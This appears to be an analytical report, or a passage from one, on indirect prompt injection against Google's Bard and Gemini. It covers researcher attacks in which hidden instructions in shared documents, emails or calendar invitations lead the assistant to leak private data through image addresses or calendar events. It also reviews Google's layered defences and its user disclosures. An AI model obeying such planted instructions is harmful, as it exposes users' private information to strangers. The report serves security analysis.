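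The outside researchers Nassi, Noma and Miggo, by contrast, tested Google's products with whatever protections were running. Like the 2023 reports, theirs give no success rates, and researchers seldom publish their failures. Capitella is an exception, because he reported the routes that Google had blocked as well as the one it had not.

In May 2025 Google's researchers reported that a hostile invitation could get Gemini 2.5 to write private data into a calendar event in up to 94.6 per cent of test conversations. In January 2026 Miggo disclosed that a similar attack worked in the product itself. Google's test altered an existing event while Miggo's attack created a new one, and the model may have changed in between. Even so, the test had pointed to a method of attack that the product's other defences evidently failed to block in time.

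### Signs of real attacks

Researchers carried out all of these attacks. Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) made the widest search for injections in actual use, in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*. They searched 1.2 billion public web addresses, mostly as recorded in an October 2025 crawl, for 3,963 phrases typical of injections, and added results from two services that scan internet servers. They reviewed the matches by hand and confirmed 15,387 injections.

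Site owners wrote many of the injections to keep AI programs from copying their pages, or to identify the programs that did. The largest group was meant to make an AI system produce nonsense. Only 13 injections, fewer than one in a thousand, were meant to extract data. Nine targeted the system's standing instructions and four targeted other secrets. Khodayari and colleagues judged that the 13 were aimed at customer-support systems and at agents that carry out tasks, so none is evidence of an attack on Bard or on a Gemini user's mailbox.

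They also tried such injections on 13 models, in 5,200 trials. The models complied in at most 8 per cent of trials when they received a page as plain text, and in about 1 per cent or less when the page kept its structure. Google's much higher rates are consistent with this, because most of the injections in the wild are blunt orders to the model to ignore its instructions, whereas Google's researchers refined theirs against the model they were attacking.

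The study searched a crawl of the public web, so it could not have found the most relevant attacks, which use hostile emails or privately shared documents. A search for known phrases would also miss instructions in unusual wording, such as Rehberger's notice from a legal department. Google's 2024 statement to SC Media is more direct evidence, since Google can examine its own records, but the statement concerned only HiddenLayer's findings. No source reports a real theft through Bard. Such attacks were probably rare in 2023, but the evidence does not show that there were none.

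### One channel or the whole weakness

Google closed the image channel, and the fix seems to have held in the consumer chatbot, since nobody in these later tests reopened the channel there. But in every successful test from November 2023 to January 2026, the assistant still treated a stranger's text as its user's instructions, which was the weakness that had made the channel dangerous.

It may be unfair to hold this against Google alone, since Shi and colleagues write that researchers generally agree that training cannot fully solve the problem. They recommend several layers of defence to make attacks harder and more expensive. By that standard Google has made progress. Its training halved the average success rate of attacks, and in one test a combination of defences cut the best attack's success rate to 6.2 per cent. Newer capabilities do not improve security by themselves. The researchers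 found that a model that follows instructions better can be easier to attack, because it also follows the attacker's instructions better.

But a low success rate protects people less when an attack is easy to repeat. If an attacker sent the same email to 100,000 people whose assistants all read it, a 6.2 per cent success rate would mean 6,200 thefts. Google's remaining protection is to limit what a deceived assistant can do, which becomes harder as Google gives Gemini more abilities. When Rehberger published his tests in 2024, he considered the danger limited for the time being because the image leak was closed and the extensions could not write anything. He expected the danger to become high if either changed. Two years later, Gemini could write to a calendar, and Miggo used the calendar to exfiltrate data.

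## What Google disclosed for later Gemini connections to Gmail, Docs and Drive

By June 2025, almost 21 months after it launched Bard Extensions, Google was warning users in help pages and security posts that other people's documents could contain instructions aimed at its assistant. Its launch posts for Deep Research and Personal Intelligence, two later features that read a user's mail, do not include this warning. Some of the defences Google described in 2025 apply to the route the Bard attacks took, but Google has not linked its new warnings to those attacks, and later events explain the timing better.

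### The launch posts

Google kept the extensions when it renamed Bard in February 2024, and it now calls them connected apps (TuttoAndroid, *Google amplia il raggio d'azione di Gemini con tante nuove App Connesse*, 2026). The best record of what Google told users at the renaming is a privacy notice dated 8 February, which mentioned adversarial prompts only as something a user might type.

On 5 November 2025 Google let Deep Research, a Gemini feature that works through many sources and writes a long report, draw on Gmail, Drive and Google Chat. Google's *Gemini Deep Research can now connect to your Gmail, Docs, Drive* (2025) consists of a few example uses and a line on how to select sources. It contains no promises about training or human review, and no warnings about errors or hostile documents.

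A day later, Google told administrators in *Gemini Deep Research now integrates with your Workspace content* (2025) that users had previously had to upload individual files from Drive by hand. This let people leave out files they didn't recognise. Deep Research could now find and read such files itself, in the same task as web pages that anyone could have written. Google presented the change as more efficient and wrote that the feature could pull "securely" from users' content.

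The Decoder's *Google's Gemini Deep Research feature now taps into Gmail, Drive, and Chat* advised caution with sensitive information. It noted that researchers had got ChatGPT's deep research mode to leak email data and had used a calendar invitation to extract data from Gemini. No reporter had written anything similar about Bard Extensions in September 2023. By late 2025, both technology reporters and Google could find several precedents.

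Google said much more about Personal Intelligence, which it launched for paying subscribers in the United States on 14 January 2026. In *Gemini introduces Personal Intelligence*, Google vice-president Woodward (2026) said that the connections were off by default, and that users could choose which apps to connect and could also chat without personalisation. He warned of inaccurate answers and of "over-personalization", in which the model connects unrelated things. For example, Gemini might infer from hundreds of photos taken at a golf course that the user likes golf, when the user only goes there because their son plays. Woodward also said that Google did not train directly on users' inboxes but did train on some prompts and answers.

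He used the word "secure" or "securely" four times. In one of these passages he argued that users don't have to send their data elsewhere to get a personal assistant, because Google already has it. This is a fair point about trusting a second company with one's mail, but it doesn't address Rehberger's attack, which carried the text from one Google service to another without the victim meaning to send it anywhere.

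For more detail, Woodward referred readers to *Building Personal Intelligence*, in which Venkatachary (2026) wrote that Google had "done work to increase resistance to prompt injections". He did not explain what a prompt injection is, how a user might encounter one, or what the work involved. He did give eight known problems of accuracy and personalisation their own headings and examples. For example, the model can attribute another person's preferences to the user, as when it infers from a receipt for a brother's concert tickets that the user likes heavy metal. Roose had encountered a similar error in Bard. Venkatachary treats the error as accidental and does not consider a sender who wants to be mistaken for the user.

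The table describes the later announcements under the same four headings as the 2023 launch post. The entry for the renaming is a privacy notice, which would have had fewer readers than a launch post.

| Date | Document | Google's use of data | Accuracy | User control | Hostile content from others |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 19 September 2023 | Pinsky's post on Bard Extensions | No human review, advertising or training with Workspace content | "Google it" button | Workspace connection is the user's choice; extensions can be turned off | Nothing |
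| 8 February 2024 | Privacy notice for the renamed Gemini | Similar promises | Lists inaccuracy as a limitation | Turning off the activity log also turns off the extensions | Only misuse by the person typing |
| 5 November 2025 | Google's post on Deep Research | Nothing | Nothing | User selects the sources | Nothing |
| 14 January 2026 | Woodward's post on Personal Intelligence | No direct training on the inbox; some training on prompts and answers | Warns of errors and over-personalisation | Off by default, with a choice for each app | Nothing |
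| September 2026 | New connected apps, as TuttoAndroid reported | Unclear from press reports | Unclear from press reports | A switch for each app | Unclear from press reports |

User control has improved in some places. In June 2026 Google let users of Ask Gemini in Drive, which answers questions about stored files, add emails as sources for a question. Shah (2026), in *Google Gemini update integrates Gmail into Google Drive searches*, reported Google's assurance that Gemini read Gmail content only when a user explicitly included email threads. An administrator also had to enable the feature. Choosing sources for each question protects users better than connecting a whole mailbox once, as Bard's users did. In Gmail, though, many of Gemini's free features were on by default in 2026, according to Engadget.

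Google has added connections faster than it has explained them. Bard Extensions had five switches. Digital Trends' *Gemini lands Adobe as a connected app*, from September 2026, lists more than 60 apps, including Google Workspace, WhatsApp, Dropbox and GitHub. Many of these can bring in text that strangers wrote. In October 2026 Google launched a workplace agent that writes and runs code, creates temporary "sub-agents" and connects to Gmail, Drive, Slack and Microsoft 365, according to CBS News' *Google launches Gemini AI workplace agent that can write code* (2026).

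### What the help pages tell users

A Google help page for people who use Gemini in Gmail, Docs and other Workspace apps now covers much of what was missing in 2023. It defines prompt injection as an attempt to get an unintended or harmful response from an AI tool. Google explains that an attacker can share malicious content with a user, who then unknowingly refers to it in a request. Gemini may refuse to answer or answer without the suspicious content. Google advises caution with shared content from unknown senders, "like files in Drive".

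The page probably first appeared between May 2024 and June 2025. The extensions help page had no such warning in May 2024. On 13 June 2025, Google described a security notice in Gemini with a "Learn more" link to a help article, and encouraged users to read the article. In its weekly summary for Workspace customers that day, Google (2025) also referred readers to the Help Center and said that people with personal accounts would be among those who got the defences. The copy of the Workspace page with the advice about Drive files dates from July 2026, so the first version may have been less complete.

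Google's page for users of the separate Gemini app, *How Gemini Apps help protect users from malicious content & prompt injection*, is harder to date. Most of its text is the same as the Workspace page's, but it mentions public Gemini chats and small web apps made with Gemini's Canvas tool instead of files in Drive. The substitution is odd because the Gemini app can also read Drive, and Rehberger used a shared document to deliver his attack on Bard. Google presents the chats and apps only as examples, so a careful reader might apply the advice to documents too.

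Google describes the threat more concretely on a third page, which is for administrators. There it explains that attackers hide malicious prompts in legitimate-looking emails and documents, and that such a prompt might be a request for the AI to share personal information. Google doesn't mention this consequence on either of the pages for users.

| | Workspace users' page | Gemini app users' page | Administrators' page |
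|---|---|---|---|
| Shared content can carry an attack | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| The attack may expose personal information | Not mentioned | Not mentioned | Yes |
| Gemini may leave out suspicious content | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Advice about strangers' content | Caution, with Drive files as an example | Caution, with public chats and Canvas apps as examples | None; users should send feedback |

The difference would matter to someone like Dana, who received a tenants' rights checklist from a stranger. She could learn from the consumer page that the checklist might make Gemini misbehave, but not that it might make Gemini send the stranger the amount of her rent. That risk is the main reason to keep the checklist out of a chat about her landlord.

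When Gemini blocks only some of the material, the user sees the notice "Some content was excluded for security reasons", according to the administrators' page. This is an improvement on 2023, when Bard's users had no comparable warning. But its wording does not identify the email or document at fault, so a user who wanted to delete it would have to work out which one it was.

Google also maintains a Privacy Hub, its main privacy document for businesses, schools and public bodies, written as a long set of questions and answers. The edition of 14 January 2026 includes a short answer about prompt injection. It says that Gemini checks for threats before performing an action and, if it finds one, notifies the user and excludes the content or blocks the action. Google launched Personal Intelligence on the same day. Organisations could not use the new feature, and the launch post for the private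 users who could didn't mention prompt injection.

By 6 October 2026, Google had limited what Gemini searches when a user is working in an externally shared file. If an employee opens a price list that a supplier can also see and asks Gemini in the side panel how the prices compare with last year's, Gemini by default reads only the price list and does not search the employee's Gmail or Drive. The same default applies to any file created outside the organisation. The employee can change the setting for a search.

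Google says the limit is meant to prevent accidental exposure, because Gemini might otherwise put something from the employee's inbox into a document that the supplier can read. The limit should also hinder a deliberate attack. If the supplier had hidden an instruction in the price list to look up the employee's mail, Gemini could not search the mail unless the employee had switched that on. But Google describes the limit for a file that the user has open. In the GeminiJack attack, the assistant itself fetched the outsider's document while answering a question, and it is unclear whether the limit would apply then.

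In both editions, Google also assures organisations that no content leaves the organisation unless a user explicitly shares it. This assurance describes how the product should work and holds only while the threat check succeeds. Miggo's calendar attack, disclosed the same month as the January edition, exposed private meetings that the user had not meant to share.

### How Google describes the defences

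Google's fullest public account of the defences is *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy*, published on 13 June 2025. It describes training the model to resist attacks, along with five other measures that operate at different points between the user's request and the answer.

Suppose Dana's checklist contains an instruction to put her rent in the address of an image. When she asks Gemini for a summary, classifiers first examine the file. These are separate machine-learning models that Google trained to recognise malicious instructions, using a catalogue of attacks it built with help from researchers in the VRP. If the classifiers flag the checklist, Gemini leaves it out or declines to answer.

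If they miss it, Gemini receives the text surrounded by reminders to carry out the user's task and ignore any instructions in the content. Google calls this "security thought reinforcement". The reminders resemble the warning that did well in the tests by Shi and colleagues, and the model can likewise fail to follow them.

If the model does fail and writes the image line, the next measure is the markdown sanitizer. It blocks any image with an external address, so Dana's browser has no reason to contact the stranger's server. For ordinary links, Gemini uses Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous websites, and replaces a suspicious address with "suspicious link removed".

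The other two measures involve the user. Gemini asks for confirmation before certain risky actions, such as deleting a calendar event, and shows the notice with the "Learn more" link when a defence has stopped something. Confirmation would not have helped against the Bard attacks, which involved no such action.

The rule on images is the most relevant to the 2023 demonstrations, and it can stop the leak even when every earlier defence has failed to recognise the attack. However, its effectiveness depends largely on what counts as "external", which Google's post does not define. Rehberger's image address belonged to Google's own script service, and Carta and Gardner's began at google.com, so a sanitizer that treated every Google address as internal would have let both through. Google presumably avoided this mistake, having already fixed the leak once. Capitella's failed attempts in 2024 suggest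 that the consumer chatbot blocked at least the variants he tried.

The rule for links is less strict because Gemini has to judge whether an address looks suspicious. A new server set up for a single theft may not have a bad reputation yet. In July 2025, a month after Google's post, a reporter whose article Startup Daily republished tried the hidden-text attack on Gmail summaries that a researcher had reported to 0din. The reporter got Gemini to tell the user that their password had been compromised and to offer a link for changing it. At about that time, a spokesperson told Dark Reading that Google was "mid-deployment" on several of the defences, according to PYMNTS's *Google AI Chatbot Target of Potential Phishing Attacks*, so some may not yet have reached the reporter's account.

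The post defined "Gemini" as the Gemini app and Gemini in Workspace, so its statement that Gemini did not load external images did not cover Gemini Enterprise, a separate product. Gemini Enterprise was loading external images at around that time, and Noma reported the resulting flaw, GeminiJack, to Google in May or June 2025.

*Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes how Google keeps its defences up to date. Google collects attacks from its own testers, automated tests, the VRP and public disclosures in a central catalogue. Staff reproduce each new attack and assign it to someone, then generate variants to retrain the classifiers and the model. Because retraining takes time, Google also has rules that it can change quickly through a configuration file. These cover confirmations, web addresses and "tool chaining", which presumably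 means which tool Gemini may use after another.

Gavish wrote that Google measures what a defence contributes by simulating attacks on Gmail, Docs and other apps with the defence on and then off. His post gives no success rates, so readers can't tell from it how often attacks still work on the finished product, although Google evidently has figures.

Google described stricter rules for addresses when Gemini gained the ability to browse websites, run code and carry out multi-step tasks. Google's *How Gemini's defense-in-depth approach works*, online by November 2026, explains that fixed rules outside the model restrict which addresses Gemini can open or send information to. Its example is a fake promotional email with hidden instructions to pull details from the user's other emails and send them to an outside link. This is almost the full attack, which nobody had demonstrated on Bard. The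 user in the example is a householder puzzled by an electricity bill, so Google had begun to explain the danger in terms that people outside security could follow.

Google is also more candid about failure in these posts than in its help pages. It wrote in the defence-in-depth post that "no detector catches every injection attempt". Gavish said that indirect prompt injection is not a problem you "solve" and move on from. Google DeepMind, the company's AI research laboratory, acknowledged in *Advancing Gemini's security safeguards* (2025) that no model is completely immune. In an earlier post on its security blog, which Willison quoted by March 2025, Google wrote that no single defence was likely to solve the problem entirely. Willison agreed, but doubted that defences based on rules of thumb would be enough to deploy such systems responsibly. The help pages tell users what happens when Gemini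 identifies an attack but have no comparable statement about the attacks it misses. They advise users to be careful, which implies that the filters are imperfect, but a user could easily conclude that Google handles the problem for them.

### Whether the Bard attacks shaped the engineering

The Bard reports almost certainly affected Google's engineering at first, since Google changed Bard within 30 days of receiving Rehberger's. Their influence on the defences of 2025 is harder to show. The sanitizer closes the same channel, and Google says it used VRP reports to build its catalogue of attacks. Both Bard attacks reached Google through the VRP and later became public, so they would qualify for the catalogue by either route, if it goes back that far.

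Gavish also mentions that Google now gives researchers invited to its live hacking events access to features before their release. Such access would have helped in 2023, but that year's contestants apparently lacked it. Google may have adopted the practice because of the Bard case, but Gavish does not say when or why it began, and companies have other reasons to test products before release.

The decision to block external images is weak evidence that engineers were responding to the Bard reports, because other attacks used the same method. Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT and Rehberger's report on Generative AI Studio both came before Bard Extensions, and either could have led engineers who had never heard of the Bard reports to make the same decision.

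In Google's research, Shi and colleagues write that their test setup mirrors early internal testing and publicly reported attacks. They cite three public attacks: Samoilenko's on ChatGPT, HiddenLayer's from 2024 on Gemini for Workspace, and Rehberger's from 2025 on Gemini's memory. They do not cite Rehberger's Bard report, but the title of his 2025 report includes "delayed tool invocation", the technique he had used on Bard in November 2023. His work on Bard may therefore have influenced the researchers indirectly, through the later attack that reused part of it.

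Shi and colleagues began their evaluations in early 2024, a few months after the Bard reports. The timing is consistent with a direct influence, but about equally consistent with the alternatives, because attacks on other assistants had also become public during 2023. The Bard reports were probably one of several cases that informed the work, and Google's published account gives no reason to rank them first.

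### Why the warnings came in 2025

The case that the attacks influenced Google's disclosures is weaker. Google first explained the risk to users almost 20 months after it confirmed the Bard fix. If the attacks had persuaded Google that users needed a warning, it would probably have added one to the extensions help page soon afterwards, but the May 2024 version of the page had none.

Google's June 2025 post said that, because of its image rule, EchoLeak did not apply to Gemini. EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that became public the same week, also used an image to send out private data. The post did not mention that Google's own chatbot had once had a similar flaw, or that Google had paid the people who found it. Google had no obvious need to hide this, as it had listed both Bard reports in its reviews of the reward program. But a post meant to reassure customers about a competitor's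 problem was an unlikely place to bring up an old problem of Google's own, so the omission is weak evidence of what the engineers remembered.

Google also called indirect prompt injection an "emerging" attack in the post. Google (2025) used the same word a month later, nearly two years after Rehberger's report, when it told administrators that Gemini's layered defences made it ready for business use. The word suggests that Google was presenting the issue as new and a result of wider AI use, rather than looking back to Bard.

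A report about Gemini fits the date better. Nassi, Cohen and Yair reported their calendar attacks to Google in February 2025, and the 90 days that Google requested ended on 23 May. Google DeepMind published its post and the paper by Shi and colleagues on 20 May, and the post on layered defences followed three weeks after the deadline. In that post Google thanked the three researchers by name, and it had also said that their report led it to speed up its work on defences. Their report is the best documented outside influence on what Google published that June, although work on this scale must have begun well before February.

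HiddenLayer's report may have contributed earlier. *New Gemini for Workspace Vulnerability Enabling Phishing & Content Manipulation* (Martin and Yeung, 2024) described the tests that Google responded to through SC Media, so the company was discussing the risk with reporters by autumn 2024.

On 12 June, a day before the post on layered defences, *Cloud CISO Perspectives* (Chuvakin, 2025) introduced a Google report on securing AI agents. Companies across the industry were starting to sell assistants that act on a user's behalf, and business customers wanted to know how safe they were. Google would have had a commercial reason to answer them in public even if nobody had ever attacked Bard.

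The simplest explanation for the help page is that Google needed a page for the "Learn more" link in Gemini's new notice. The 2023 fix, as far as Rehberger could tell, was a filter that ordinary users would not have noticed. The 2025 defences sometimes remove an email from a summary or stop Gemini from answering, and users would want to know why. Google also said the notices were meant to help people watch out for similar attacks.

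If this is right, the Bard reports could still have affected disclosure indirectly, by contributing to defences that Google later had to explain. It would also explain why Google put the warnings where users land after Gemini has blocked something, and on pages for people looking for security information. Google had no similar practical need to warn users when they connected an app. Neither Woodward's invitation to connect Gmail in January 2026 nor Pinsky's in September 2023 included a warning.
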